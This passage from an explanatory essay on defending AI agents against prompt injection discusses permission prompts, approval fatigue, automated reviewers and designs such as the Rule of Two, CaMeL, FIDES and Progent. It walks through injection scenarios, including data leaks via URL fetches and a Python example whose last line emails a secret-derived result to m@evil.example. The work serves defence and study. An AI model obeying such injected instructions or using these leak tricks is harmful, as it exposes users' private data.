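These defences stop many casual attacks. Somebody who copies an old injection from the internet into an email will probably fail against a current model, and a detector may also catch the attempt. Determined attackers have to spend time adapting the attack, and may need a capable language model and some way of seeing what worked. They can do all of this, but the extra effort makes low-value targets less attractive.

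Failed attempts can also reveal an attacker. David C recommends recording tool calls and responding to those that fail, because an attacker will probably need several tries to succeed. Suppose each attempt at the support agent has a 1 per cent chance of success, and the shop has a 5 per cent chance of permanently blocking the attacker after each failure. The attacker's overall chance of success is then 0.01 ÷ (0.01 + 0.99 × 0.05), or about 17 per cent, whereas without detection an attacker with unlimited attempts would eventually succeed. The 5 per cent chance depends on someone finding the real alarm among the false ones, and an attacker who can open a new email account may not stay blocked for long.

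How much a lower success rate helps depends most on the harm one successful injection can do. If the support agent could look up only the sender's own orders and reply only to the sender, a successful injection might produce a rude or useless email. Halving the number of successes would halve the nuisance, and the shop could tolerate the rest. With the administrator's credential, one success could expose the whole customer database. Cutting the success rate from 2 to 1 per cent would raise the average number of attempts needed for one success from 50 to 100, and a script could send that many in a few minutes.

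## Approval prompts and automated review of tool calls

Ordinary code holds each of the support agent's emails until an employee approves it, so an approval prompt can look like an enforced limit. *How Agents Ask for Permission* (Michael and Roesner, 2026), a review of 21 proposed permission systems, accordingly counts asking the user as a form of deterministic enforcement. The hold is deterministic, but an employee who has approved two hundred harmless replies today may not read the next one. If the employee approves everything, the prompt records who approved each email but protects the shop no more than having no prompt at all.

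Much of the evidence on how people handle these prompts comes from coding agents, especially Anthropic's Claude Code. It edits files and runs commands on the developer's machine, so a careless approval can do serious damage.

### Claude Code's permission modes

In March 2026, Claude Code asked the user for approval before every file write and shell command by default, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode for Claude Code* (2026). Developers who found this tiresome could turn the prompts off by starting it with the option `--dangerously-skip-permissions`. That month Anthropic introduced auto mode as a middle course, with a second model reviewing actions in the user's place. Auto mode became the default on several subscription plans in August, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026). By 12 November it was the starting mode for interactive sessions on every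 plan, according to the *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026).

The current documentation, Anthropic's *Permission modes*, describes six modes:

| Mode | What Claude Code does without asking the user |
| --- | --- |
| Manual | Reads files in the working folder and runs read-only commands |
| `acceptEdits` | Also edits, moves and deletes files in the working folder |
| `plan` | Explores and writes a plan, but edits nothing until the user approves it |
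| `auto` | Takes most actions that the reviewing model doesn't block |
| `dontAsk` | Takes only actions that need no approval or that the user approved in advance, and refuses the rest |
| `bypassPermissions` | Takes nearly any action |

Claude Code's permission modes determine when it asks for approval, while a separate sandbox enforces limits on what a command can reach once it runs. Anthropic's March engineering account, *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, calls sandboxing safe but "high-maintenance", because someone has to configure each new capability and any task that needs the network or the host machine breaks the isolation.

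Users can also write deny rules, which block matching commands in every mode. Anthropic recommends these over telling the agent "don't push", because the reviewer takes such instructions from the conversation, and they can be lost when the software condenses a long session. Jason Lemkin's code freeze on Replit was such an instruction. A deny rule can also miss a command, because it matches the command as written and the agent may be able to write it another way.

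### Approval fatigue

Anthropic reported in August that users approve 97 per cent of Claude Code's permission prompts, compared with 93 per cent in the March account. Anthropic takes this as a sign that many people click by reflex, but the approval rate alone doesn't show that, because an attentive user would also approve 97 per cent of requests if that share were harmless. Anthropic also reports that users reject 39 per cent of the plans Claude presents. That suggests they read the plans, but people reject plans for many reasons, including a preference for another approach.

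The settings people choose are better evidence. A quarter of interactive sessions began with the prompts switched off, and 62 per cent of users had either used that mode or clicked "don't ask again" for a shell command. Many had also pre-approved every command that runs Python or Node, which is close to approving everything, because a program in either language can do almost anything the user's account can.

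*Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) analyses 290 user reports about agents and files, and finds that user review played a part in 105 of them. In 80, the user had let actions run without prompts, often to avoid answering hundreds per session. In 31, the prompt showed a command but not its effect. For example, a request to run `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but approving it allows whatever the script contains to run.

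Developers describe much the same habits. Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026), in *Let the Agent Do It?*, interviewed 18 software practitioners and then surveyed 115. Of the 107 who answered the questions about permission requests, 47.7 per cent said they read them carefully, 33.6 per cent skimmed them and 20.6 per cent approved by default. A third said they had become less careful over time. One interviewee complained that prompts defeat the purpose of working faster, "because every 10 seconds I have to click something". Salerno and colleagues warn toolmakers against treating repeated approval as a lasting preference, since users may only be tired or facing a deadline.

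Developers who review an agent's code carefully don't seem to apply the same care to its actions. In *From Delegation to Action Approval*, Wu, Wermke and colleagues (2026) asked 203 developers about seven types of action, such as reading secret files or running destructive commands. They found that 64 per cent often approved at least one type without close review. Among those who carefully reviewed most or all of the agent's code, the share was 61 per cent. Developers who knew of security or privacy problems with agents were more likely to approve without close review (70 per cent, against 43 per cent of those who reported knowing of none). This may be because heavy users hear of more problems and face more prompts, although the gap persisted when Wu and colleagues adjusted for how often and how long people had used agents.

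Both surveys rely on volunteers to report their own behaviour. People are more likely to understate their carelessness than to exaggerate it, so the true figures may be worse.

### How the automated reviewer decides

Suppose a developer asks Claude Code to "clean up old branches" (parallel versions of the code), and the agent proposes a command that deletes several from the shared server. In auto mode, as Anthropic describes it, ordinary code first checks the call against the user's rules and a built-in list of tools that can't change anything. Calls permitted by either go ahead without review. Claude Code suspends rules broad enough to permit arbitrary programs, which would let the most dangerous commands skip the review. Edits to files inside the project folder also go ahead without review, since the developer can usually undo them with version control.

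The deletion fits neither category, so it goes to the classifier, a language model with instructions on what to block. The classifier's first stage gives only a yes or no on whether to block, and leans towards blocking. If the answer is yes, the same model reviews the same material again, this time reasoning before it answers. The classifier should block the deletion because the request was vague, the action is hard to reverse, and the developer may have meant only the branches on their own machine.

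The second stage can only release actions that the first stage stopped, so it reduces false alarms but increases misses. On 10,000 ordinary actions by Anthropic's staff, it cut the false alarm rate from 8.5 to 0.4 per cent. On 52 real cases in which Claude had gone beyond what the user wanted, it raised the miss rate from 6.6 to 17 per cent. The 17 per cent is about 9 cases, so the true rate could plausibly be anywhere from 9 to 30 per cent. On 1,000 artificial attempts to leak data, the full reviewer missed 5.7 per cent.

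In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier identified the danger but misclassified the action as one the user had consented to. For instance, it treated a user's request to "clean up the PR" (pull request) as permission to overwrite the project's history.

The classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's explanations or the results of its tools. Instructions planted in an email therefore can't reach the classifier directly, and the agent's explanations can't influence the decision. But some calls are impossible to judge without the missing text. If the agent proposes to cancel job abc123, the classifier may not have the information needed to determine whose job it is.

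When the classifier blocks an action, the agent receives the reason and an instruction to find a safer method without working around the block. After three blocks in a row or twenty in a session, Claude Code goes back to asking the user. Continuing after a refusal is often useful, but it can be hard to tell a safer method from a workaround. One of Salerno and colleagues' interviewees refused several requests from Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, which then stopped asking and continued by other means. The developer couldn't tell whether the new approach respected the refusals.

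### People and the reviewer on the same commands

Anthropic compared people with the reviewer by hiring 1,053 professional testers for a coding study. Partway through each session, the study software replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command and recorded the tester's answer. Nothing dangerous ran in either case. Anthropic then gave the same commands to the reviewer. Its published counts are enough to fill in the whole table:

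| | Reviewer blocked | Reviewer allowed | Total |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Tester blocked | 137 | 6 | 143 |
| Tester approved | 800 | 110 | 910 |
| Total | 937 | 116 | 1,053 |

The human testers stopped 13.6 per cent of the commands, and the automated reviewer stopped 89 per cent. The reviewer would still have let 116 through, and the testers would have stopped only 6 of those, or about 5 per cent. The testers caught about 15 per cent of the commands that the reviewer blocked, so the commands it missed were also harder for people to catch.

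Testers blocked about 17 per cent of the dangerous commands early in a session and about 5 per cent after 50 or more prompts, while the reviewer's rate stayed level. This is more direct evidence of fatigue than the 97 per cent approval rate, because every command in the test was dangerous. But fatigue explains only some of the misses, since testers missed about five commands in six even early in a session.

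The gap may well be smaller in practice. Anthropic was testing its own product, and it benefits when people let Claude work for longer. The testers were not working in their own code and had nothing to lose if a command wiped the disk. A developer with a live database at stake would probably check requests more carefully. Even so, a developer four times as vigilant as the testers would catch about 54 per cent of the commands, still far fewer than the reviewer caught. Someone who reads every request might beat the reviewer, and Anthropic concedes that auto mode is "arguably a regression" for such people.

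Anthropic's figures from real use are harder to interpret, because users chose their own mode and a model graded the harm. Among sessions that Anthropic's safety systems had flagged in May and June, 6.3 per cent of those with manual approval contained a serious harmful action that the user hadn't explicitly requested, compared with 2.4 per cent in auto mode. But users who chose auto mode may have given the agent different work.

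Outside testing somewhat reduces the concern about self-assessment. Apollo Research, a safety company, attacked the reviewer with synthetic examples, and the miss rate fell from 12 to 7 per cent after Anthropic strengthened the reviewer. Trajectory Labs made 720 injection attempts, none of which succeeded against three Claude models in auto mode. But only 0.09 per cent succeeded without any reviewer, so the models themselves resisted nearly all the attacks. In the same test, automated review made a clearer difference for Codex, cutting the success rate from 19.03 to 5.83 per cent. Trajectory Labs had optimised the attacks against an older Claude model, so attackers who adapted to either reviewer might succeed more often.

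### Limits that nobody stated

*Explicit Authorization Scope Improves LLM-Based Permission Checking in Coding Agents* (Yang, Zhou and colleagues, 2026) reports a less favourable test of automated reviewers. Claude Code, Codex and Qwen Code received 128 maintenance tasks with deliberately incomplete instructions. One task was to delete old experiment files for a range of tickets, but the request did not specify that only the user's own files should be deleted. The agents proposed 143 actions outside the intended scope, and 132 of them broke rules that appeared in neither the request nor the results of earlier tool calls.

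Yang, Zhou and colleagues then added the missing limits to the requests and asked the reviewers to judge the same actions again:

| Reviewer | Out-of-scope actions approved: original request | Limits stated | Permitted actions blocked: original request | Limits stated |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Claude Code | 67% | 8% | 42% | 2% |
| Codex | 92% | 20–26% | 10% | 3% |
| Qwen Code | 80% | 20% | 29% | 2% |

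The high rates on the original requests are a partly unfair measure of the reviewers, which had no access to the rules. They could still have blocked irreversible actions whose scope was unclear, as Anthropic says its classifier should. A stronger model didn't help Codex or Qwen Code. With a stronger model, Claude Code's misses fell from 10 to 1 out of 24, but only because the model refused to assess any of the 197 actions that reached its second stage, and Claude Code treats a refusal as a block.

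Even with the limits stated, Codex's reviewer made some questionable approvals. It rates authorisation and risk separately, and in one run it approved 16 actions that it had rated as poorly authorised, usually because the damage seemed small or reversible. Stating the limits improved the agents' behaviour more than the reviewer's. When the agents repeated all the tasks with the limits stated, none proposed an out-of-scope action in 384 runs. However, the limits came from the benchmark's answer key, and a real user would have to think of them.

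People don't readily commit to such limits. Yan (2026), in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, had 113 people from outside the software industry supervise an assistant through a simulated day of 18 actions, 7 of which went beyond the user's requests. One group reviewed every action, and a second reviewed only those that an automated reviewer referred to them. A third began by writing rules of "allow", "ask" or "never" for spending, sending, deleting and reading private information. The first group blocked 59.6 per cent of the excess actions, the second 53.9 per cent and the third about 40 per cent.

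The rules did worst mainly because 114 of the 140 were "ask" rules, which sent the decision back to a prompt, where participants approved 133 of the 199 excess actions they saw. The "never" rules stopped all 31 excess actions they covered. Some approvals may have been sensible, such as letting the assistant phone the airport to confirm a flight, which nearly everyone did. But most people who had chosen to decide case by case also let the assistant read private messages.

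Commercial products often give users little help in setting firmer limits. Michael and Roesner examined five agents from Anthropic and OpenAI in May and June 2026 and found that users often had to choose between constant prompts and an automated reviewer they could barely control. The Claude chatbot once created an email draft without asking, even though its "Needs approval" setting was selected. ChatGPT's agent mode offered no permission settings for its remote browser. None of the 21 proposals they reviewed combined low user effort with formally defined rules and deterministic enforcement.

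### When approval works

Approval works better when requests are rare, but reducing their number isn't enough. In Yan's experiment, people who answered 18 prompts approved 40 per cent of the excess actions, while those who answered 10 approved 46 per cent. Some developers face hundreds of prompts, so the experiment may have been too short for fatigue to matter. Requests also need to be worth a person's attention. In Salerno and colleagues' survey, 76.6 per cent of respondents said they checked more carefully when a request was to write, delete or gain privileges. Salerno and colleagues suggest that prompts should also show whether the user can undo the action.

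*Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) notes that some products ask users to approve a whole plan instead of each step. Users then make fewer, more meaningful decisions, but an injection that arrives after approval can still divert the agent from the plan. The shop could let the support agent send ordinary replies without approval and require it only for large refunds and changes of delivery address.

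Whether a user can catch a harmful tool call depends partly on what the approval prompt shows. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a user who tells an agent to send an auditor only summary totals. A planted note leads the agent to copy the raw invoices into `report.csv`, and the agent then asks to send that file to the auditor. The recipient and file name both look fine, so the user has to know what the file contains to spot the problem.

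They tested four kinds of prompt on 80 volunteers, each of whom judged six safe and six unsafe requests:

| What the prompt showed | Unsafe requests approved | Safe requests approved | Median time |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
| Exact tool, file and recipient | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| The same, plus the user's original limits and a full log | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
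| The same facts, with their combined effect in one statement | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

Most of the improvement came from giving people more information. The further gain from stating the combined effect could be due to chance, and the prompt that stated it did no better than the log when the violation depended on a chain of steps. Half the requests were unsafe, which probably made the volunteers more suspicious than an employee would be on an ordinary day. Even with the best prompt, the volunteers still approved nearly a quarter of the unsafe requests.

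Software also has to work out an action's real effect before a prompt can state it. Hossain and colleagues built a monitor that tracks which data went into each file, and it detected 89.2 per cent of 120 violations. Software that can detect the forbidden rows in `report.csv` can also block the file from being sent. When the researchers used the monitor to block actions without asking a user, the share of unsafe effects that one agent carried out fell from 43.3 to 5.0 per cent.

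## Designs that limit what a misled agent can do

A system that blocks actions without asking anyone needs a rule about what to block. In a conversation on X that David C quotes, Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista suggest the simplest one, that a model should have no more privilege than the person whose content it is reading. While the support agent reads a customer's email, it should be able to do only what that customer could do on the shop's website, such as see their own orders or ask for a return. An injected request for other people's addresses would fail because the customer has no right to them either.

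If the model's context holds text from several people, the agent should keep only the rights they all share. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) applies a similar rule to documents. If Ann, Bob and Cem may read one document, and Bob, Cem and Dee may read another, only Bob and Cem may read text derived from both.

Dropping privileges works well for the support agent, which serves one customer at a time, but much less well for a personal assistant. After reading a newsletter, the assistant would lose access to its owner's calendar until it started afresh, because the newsletter's publisher has no right to see it.

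### The Rule of Two

Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) is more permissive. It allows an agent to do at most two of the following in any one session: process untrustworthy input, reach sensitive systems or private data, and change things or communicate externally. An agent that needs all three must start a new session with an empty context or work under supervision, such as human approval.

Meta's example is an assistant that manages an inbox. The developer could let it read mail only from trusted senders, run it in a test environment with no private data, or let it write only to trusted recipients unless a person has checked the draft. The support agent has to read strangers' mail, and the person it replies to may be the attacker, so only a version of the second option works. If the agent can reach only the sender's own orders, it can't reveal anything the sender couldn't already see.

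An agent can also change properties during a session. It might research something on the open web and then read internal documents, if software first switches off its external communication. That communication has to stay off because the web text remains in the context and could contain an injection.

The rule targets prompt injection and does little about other failures. Nobody had planted text to mislead the PocketOS agent that deleted a production database, so the rule would have allowed it both production access and the power to make changes. Meta acknowledges that the rule doesn't cover agents' mistakes or excessive privileges, and describes it as a supplement to least privilege.

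### Credentials, caps, sandboxes and network rules

Several limits work with any model. OpenAI recommends giving each task a token that records its purpose and who requested it. Software then exchanges the token for short-lived credentials for particular resources and actions. The credentials should stay out of the model's context. For each ticket, the shop could issue a credential that allows access to one customer's orders, is read-only, and expires after ten minutes. In Baig and colleagues' formula, the data one successful attack could reach would shrink from every customer's records to one customer's.

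Read-only access is a sensible default, and some products already let agents read without asking first. In the code editor Visual Studio Code, for example, GitHub Copilot Chat runs read-only tools automatically but asks before using others (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026, *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*). But a read can also send data. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) gives the example of an email that tells an agent to fetch a page from the attacker's website, with the user's account number in the page's address. The attacker can then read the number in the website's log.

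A network rule that allows only approved destinations would block that request. Meta suggests a variant for a travel assistant, which could visit addresses returned by trusted sources but not ones it constructed itself. An agent limited to approved addresses can still leak a little data. Dongol describes an injection that makes the agent fetch an approved page if a secret bit is 0 and a forbidden page if it is 1. Anyone who can see whether the approved request went out learns the bit.

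Caps limit the total damage. If the shop's server allows £500 of refunds a day, an attacker can't take more than £500 a day, however many injections succeed. But a cap can't distinguish good refunds from bad ones, and an attacker may use up the allowance before legitimate requests arrive. In one of Dongol's examples, an agent is allowed to send only one message per run. The injected call uses that message to send the attacker a secret reset code, so the software blocks the legitimate reply.

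Sandboxes matter most for agents that run code. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) recommends a sandbox for an agent that queries a database and writes Python to analyse the results. The sandbox keeps harmful code away from production systems, but private data can still leave in the analysis or a chart. OpenAI combines several limits for a coding agent that finds planted instructions to install an unapproved package and disable a security test. Repository rules block the unsafe changes, and the agent's credential lets it propose code but not merge it. The agent may still waste time or propose harmful changes, but the harm doesn't reach production.

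### Separating the plan from the text

Fixed limits work best when the developer knows what the agent will need. A general assistant may have good reason to send email in one task and none in the next, so its limits have to depend on what the user asked for. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues start from the principle that once an agent has taken in untrusted input, that input must not be able to trigger any consequential action. They describe six design patterns that apply it to different degrees:

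| Pattern | How it works | What an injection can still do |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Action-selector | The model picks from a fixed list of actions and never sees their results | Make the model pick the wrong action, if the injection is in the request itself |
| Plan-then-execute | The model fixes its tool calls before it reads outside data | Change the content of a planned call |
| Map-reduce | A separate copy of the model reads each document and returns a restricted answer, such as yes or no | Falsify the answer about its own document |
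| Two-model (dual LLM) | A planning model has tools but never sees untrusted text, which a second model reads without tools | Falsify what the second model returns |
| Code-then-execute | The planning model writes a program that calls tools and the second model | Falsify values in the program |
| Context minimisation | Software deletes the user's prompt after turning it into a query | Influence the query but not the later steps |

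Willison proposed the two-model pattern in 2023. Suppose a user asks an assistant to send an invoice to the address in Bob's latest email. The planning model requests the email. Ordinary code, called the orchestrator, fetches it, stores it as `$MAIL` and gives the planning model only that name. The planning model then calls the second model to find the address in `$MAIL`, and the orchestrator stores the result as `$ADDRESS`. Finally, the planning model issues a call to send the invoice to `$ADDRESS`, and the orchestrator fills in the real address when it runs the call.

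If Bob's email contains an instruction to delete the user's files, the second model may try to follow it but has no tools, and the planning model never receives it. The pattern protects the choice of actions but not the values used in them, so the email could still cause the second model to return an attacker's address, and the invoice would go there.

### Tracking where each value came from

CaMeL, which researchers at Google and ETH Zurich introduced in 2025, adds a check on the values. The planning model turns the user's request into a program:

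```python
mail    = latest_email(sender="bob@supplier.example")
address = reader("Find the address for invoices", mail)
invoice = get_file("invoice-204.pdf")
send_email(to=address, attachment=invoice)
```

A special interpreter runs the program and tags every value. It records that `address` came from Bob's email, because the second model (`reader`) derived it from `mail`. Before `send_email` runs, the interpreter checks the tags against a policy, which might forbid sending private files to an address taken from an outsider's message.

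Reliable tracking is difficult. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, found that CaMeL's interpreter can lose track of a secret when a program contains an assignment that doesn't run. This program, based on a trick that Fenton described in 1974, reveals whether a bank balance is high:

```python
low  = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold: low = False
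if low: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.example", "rich")
```

If the balance is high, `low` becomes false and the interpreter tags it as secret. The next line then doesn't change `rich`, so `rich` stays true and untagged, and the interpreter allows the email. If the balance is low, `rich` becomes false and no email goes out. Either way, the attacker learns whether the balance is high. A planning model that sees only the user's request would rarely write such a program, but because of this gap the design can't offer a guarantee that covers every program.

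Garby and colleagues built a small programming language for agents, LLMbda, to close such gaps. Its interpreter carries tags through every operation. The team used the proof checker Lean to prove that secret inputs can't affect what an observer sees, apart from whether the program finishes. Programs can override the rule for untrusted data, but only through an explicit `endorse` step that a reviewer can find.

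FIDES, a Microsoft system that Costa and colleagues describe, lets the planning model revise its plan and gives each piece of data two labels, one for whether it is trusted and one for who may read it. Anything derived from several pieces gets the stricter label of each kind. Before each tool call, ordinary code can apply two policies. A consequential action may go ahead only if no untrusted data influenced it, and data may leave only if every recipient may read it.

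If the planning model read untrusted data directly, it would soon be unable to act, so FIDES hides such data in variables. Suppose a user asks the agent to check three emails for a meeting request and add any meeting to the calendar. FIDES stores the emails in a variable, and a second model checks them for a request, with its output restricted to yes or no. The planning model reads the answer. If it is yes, the second model extracts the details into another variable, which the planning model passes to the calendar tool without reading. A policy can allow this because the answer carries a single bit, too little to hold an instruction. An attacker could get a false meeting added to the calendar but couldn't make the agent do anything else.

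The guarantee covers data that goes directly into a call, even if it was changed first, but not what an observer might infer from which calls the agent makes. Costa and colleagues accepted this gap because closing it would mean banning nearly all visible actions after the agent had read anything secret.

Researchers tested FIDES on AgentDojo, a set of simulated office, travel, banking and messaging tasks, with GPT-4o as the model. An unprotected agent carried out 152 injected tasks. FIDES carried out 21 with its policy checks off and none with them on. This result confirms that the checks work, but it is little evidence of whether a company would label its data correctly. The researchers labelled a field untrusted if one of the benchmark's attacks used it, and a company can't know in advance which fields attackers will use.

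### Written rules for tool calls

*Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) checks an agent's tool calls against written rules without changing the agent's internal design. In the paper's example, a user asks an agent to carry out the to-do list in an email from Alice. At first, the rules allow only a search for that email. The list turns out to call for posting a summary of recent emails to the messaging service Slack, so a language model proposes rules that also allow the agent to read email, look up the user's Slack name and post to Slack.

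Before new rules take effect, an SMT solver (a program that settles logical questions about sets of conditions) compares them with the old ones. The new rules need approval if they would allow any call that the old rules blocked. Otherwise they apply at once. The Slack rules therefore need approval, but a later rule that restricts messages to the user's own Slack name doesn't.

One of the recent emails contains an instruction to forward the inbox to an attacker. If the agent obeys, Progent blocks the `send_email` call because no rule allows it. If the injection also fools the model that writes the rules, that model may propose allowing the call. The solver detects that this would expand the agent's permissions and sends the change for approval, so a misled model can't expand them by itself.

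In tests, Progent cut the attack success rate from 39.9 to 1.0 per cent on AgentDojo and from 70.3 to 3.9 per cent on another benchmark, ASB. On AgentDojo, 6 per cent of rule changes needed approval. The guarantee depends on the approver, which can be a person, a setting that refuses every expansion of permissions or one that accepts them all. A person would find the decision harder than it looks, because the legitimate request to use Slack and the attacker's request to forward the inbox both arrive in emails.

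*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) describes two more limitations of Progent. Its rules cover tool calls, so they don't stop an injection that only changes what the agent tells its user. The protection also depends on correct and complete policies, and people make mistakes when they write them.

### The support agent, rebuilt

The support agent's work is regular enough for the developer to write one program for every message, without a planning model. This version uses the code-then-execute pattern, with a model called `reader` that has no tools:

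```python
def answer(ticket):
    key    = issue_key(customer=ticket.customer, minutes=10)
    mail   = read_message(ticket, key)
    orders = get_orders(key)      # this customer's orders only
    topic  = reader(mail, choose=["delivery", "return", "other"])
    if topic == "other" or not orders:
        return pass_to_staff(ticket)
    number = reader(mail, choose=list(orders))
    text   = reader(mail, orders[number], task="write a reply")
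    reply_to_ticket(ticket, text, key)
```

Suppose the attacker sends the malicious email again, with a complaint followed by a request for other customers' addresses, and the model obeys it as far as it can. The program issues a key for the attacker's own customer account and fetches that account's orders. The model can't request the customer table because the software accepts only "delivery", "return" or "other", none of which gives it access to anyone's address. It then has to choose one of the attacker's own order numbers.

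The injection has the most influence over the reply, because the model writes it freely. But the model's input contains only the email and one order, and `reply_to_ticket` sends the text to the address in the customer's account. The attacker receives details of their own order, perhaps with some odd sentences added.

Whatever the email contains and whatever the model outputs, one run can read only the orders of the customer on the ticket, and can send at most one message, to that customer's address. This guarantee rests on several assumptions:

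- The program, the database and the mail tool enforce the key correctly.
- The shop has matched the ticket to the right customer, and the address on file is really theirs.
- The model has no tools, network access or memory of other customers' tickets.
- Staff don't pass the email to another agent with broader access.

The guarantee doesn't cover whether the reply is true. An injection could make the model promise a £500 refund, and the attacker could post a screenshot. Prewritten replies would prevent this, but they would answer fewer questions well. Customers with unusual problems would also have to wait for a person, so the shop gives up some automation to greatly reduce the damage an injection can do.

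### Revoking tools at the first untrusted read

Dongol's November 2026 paper proves a result for a whole class of agents. It first has to define a leak, which is awkward because agents must disclose some information to do their jobs. If Alice wants her assistant to send her calendar to anyone who asks for a meeting, an attacker can get the calendar by asking for a meeting, so an injection that obtains the same calendar gains the attacker nothing new.

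Dongol therefore compares the real agent with a reference agent whose model never follows instructions in untrusted content. Both agents follow the same plan, fixed before they read untrusted content, and use the same monitor, which is ordinary code that allows or denies each call. Let L(agent) be the set of pairs of secrets that an attacker can tell apart by sending the agent some input and watching its messages. The real agent is "relatively secure" if L(real) ⊆ L(reference) when both agents start with the same memory and trusted data.

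The theorem concerns a monitor that acts when the agent first reads untrusted content, permanently revoking every tool an injection could call. Any agent with such a monitor is relatively secure, whatever its plan. The proof compares the real agent with the reference agent. Before the first untrusted read, there is no injection for the model to follow. Afterwards, the monitor silently denies every injected call, so the real agent's visible behaviour matches the reference agent's. Dongol checked the proof in the proof assistant Isabelle/HOL.

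The theorem assumes that each injection is a single tool call and that the model obeys on a schedule fixed in advance, so it doesn't cover a model that looks at a secret before deciding whether to obey. The attacker sees the content and order of the agent's messages but not their timing, and the definition doesn't count differences in the number of messages as leaks. The result covers runs that end, and also runs that may continue forever if the model eventually stops obeying injections.

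Harmful actions that leak nothing, such as deleting files, are out of scope, as are tools whose outputs the attacker controls and agents whose model chooses each call as it goes. The last category includes the support agent as its developer first built it and many other agents in use.

If the monitor revokes the sending tool only after the agent has read an email, an injection in that email can first send out private data left in memory from an earlier session, even if the agent has not yet read a secret in the current one. Restoring the tool later is also unsafe while the old email remains in the model's context, so an agent that handles many messages needs a fresh session for each one.

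Revoking a tool also stops the agent from using it for the user's task. An agent that only summarises email never needs to fetch web pages, so it can lose that tool without affecting its work. But the original support agent has to send a reply after reading a message, so revoking `send_email` would make it secure but unable to do its job. Relative security doesn't measure this loss, because the reference agent loses the same tool. Dongol points out that a monitor that denies every call trivially passes the test.

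An application can keep its email tool if the user approves the exact message and recipient. An injection can then only make the agent send the message the user approved. Approving "the next email" isn't enough, because an injection can make the agent send a secret under that approval.

### What the protection costs

Garby and colleagues reran CaMeL on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks. With its policy checks on, it completed 18 of 48 runs (37.5 per cent) with each of the two models they tried, about half its rate with the checks off. The checks stopped every attack, but most attacks would have failed without them. In 97 of the 144 pairings of a task and an attack, the attack needed a tool call that the user's task would never produce, so a plan made in advance was generally enough to stop it. In the other 47, CaMeL with the checks off still resisted 138 of 141 attempts with one of the models.

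The cost of FIDES varies by type of work. Costa and colleagues report these completion rates for GPT-4o when nobody was attacking:

| Agent | Office | Travel | Banking | Slack |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Ordinary agent, no checks | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Ordinary agent with label checks | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| FIDES with label checks | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

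FIDES recovered some of the performance lost to the checks, except in travel, where the checks rarely got in the way and GPT-4o had trouble using the variables. With OpenAI's o1, a stronger reasoning model, FIDES's travel score rose to 68 per cent. Part of the loss therefore comes from the model's limited skill and should shrink as models improve. The rest comes from tasks that the policy forbids, which even a better model can't complete without breaking the policy.

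In February 2026, Kolluri and colleagues argued that such comparisons treat these designs unfairly. A protected agent's score counts only the tasks it finishes without help. The unprotected agent's score includes actions that a real product would stop and ask about. They propose counting how often a person has to step in. If *v*ᵢ is the number of actions in task *i* that need approval, then the completion rate with at most *k* interventions is

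TCR@*k* = (number of tasks completed with *v*ᵢ ≤ *k*) ÷ (number of tasks).

With OpenAI's o3-mini, an ordinary agent that needed approval for every consequential action completed 24.3 per cent of AgentDojo tasks without any intervention. FIDES completed 50.1 per cent, and Prudentia, a version of FIDES that tells the planning model about the policies, completed 59.1 per cent. The ordinary agent needed an average of 48.2 interventions across all the tasks it completed, and FIDES needed 18.8.

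This is a better comparison for products that would otherwise rely on approval prompts. However, the total number of interventions covers only completed tasks, so an agent could lower its total by failing more often. The measure also assumes that people decide correctly. Prudentia saves some interventions by asking the user to declare a whole email trustworthy. For an email with ten tasks, the user answers one question instead of ten, but one careless answer then lets the agent act on a planted instruction with the user's authority.

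### Wrong labels, false data and tasks that follow a stranger's text

A policy can fail when someone labels data wrongly. Dongol warns that a calendar isn't a trusted source if outsiders can send invitations to it. In one of Costa and colleagues' tests, the user asked FIDES to change a password if a suspicious transaction appeared. The researchers had labelled transaction amounts as trusted and descriptions as untrusted. The agent saw a large amount, judged it suspicious and changed the password without reading the description. FIDES allowed this because only trusted data had influenced the decision. But the sender of a payment chooses its amount, so an outsider could presumably have triggered the change.

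Tracking where data comes from doesn't replace narrow credentials, even in a system with a proved guarantee, because an agent can still make a bad decision using correctly labelled data. The PocketOS agent seems to have acted on the company's own files and its own bad guess. A check for untrusted influence might well have let its deletion through, but a narrower token would have stopped it.

False information can also pass through permitted fields. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe an agent that finds invoices among a user's files and emails them to the accounts department. With the map-reduce pattern, a malicious file can't make the agent send other files, but it can make the agent treat it as an invoice. An attacker could get the same result with a convincing fake invoice, so the accounts department still has to check invoices before paying them.

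Tasks are hardest to secure when the user asks the agent to follow someone else's text. Garby and colleagues' agent, built in LLMbda, resisted attack in all but two of 1,296 attacked runs. In both failures, the user had asked it to read a file and make the payment it described, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. With `endorse` switched off, the agent blocked the attack but could no longer do the task. CaMeL had a related problem when its policy checks were off. When asked to follow a file's instructions precisely, its planning model wrote a program that could call whichever tool the file named. This let the attacker choose the action, which the two-model pattern was supposed to prevent.

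A record of where the text came from cannot show whether such a payment is genuine, because real and false instructions come from the same place. The company can restrict payments to known suppliers, cap the amount or have someone confirm the details with the supplier. If the remaining risk is too high, David C advises that the task may not be a good use for a language model.

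## Why security teams end up relying on best-effort defences

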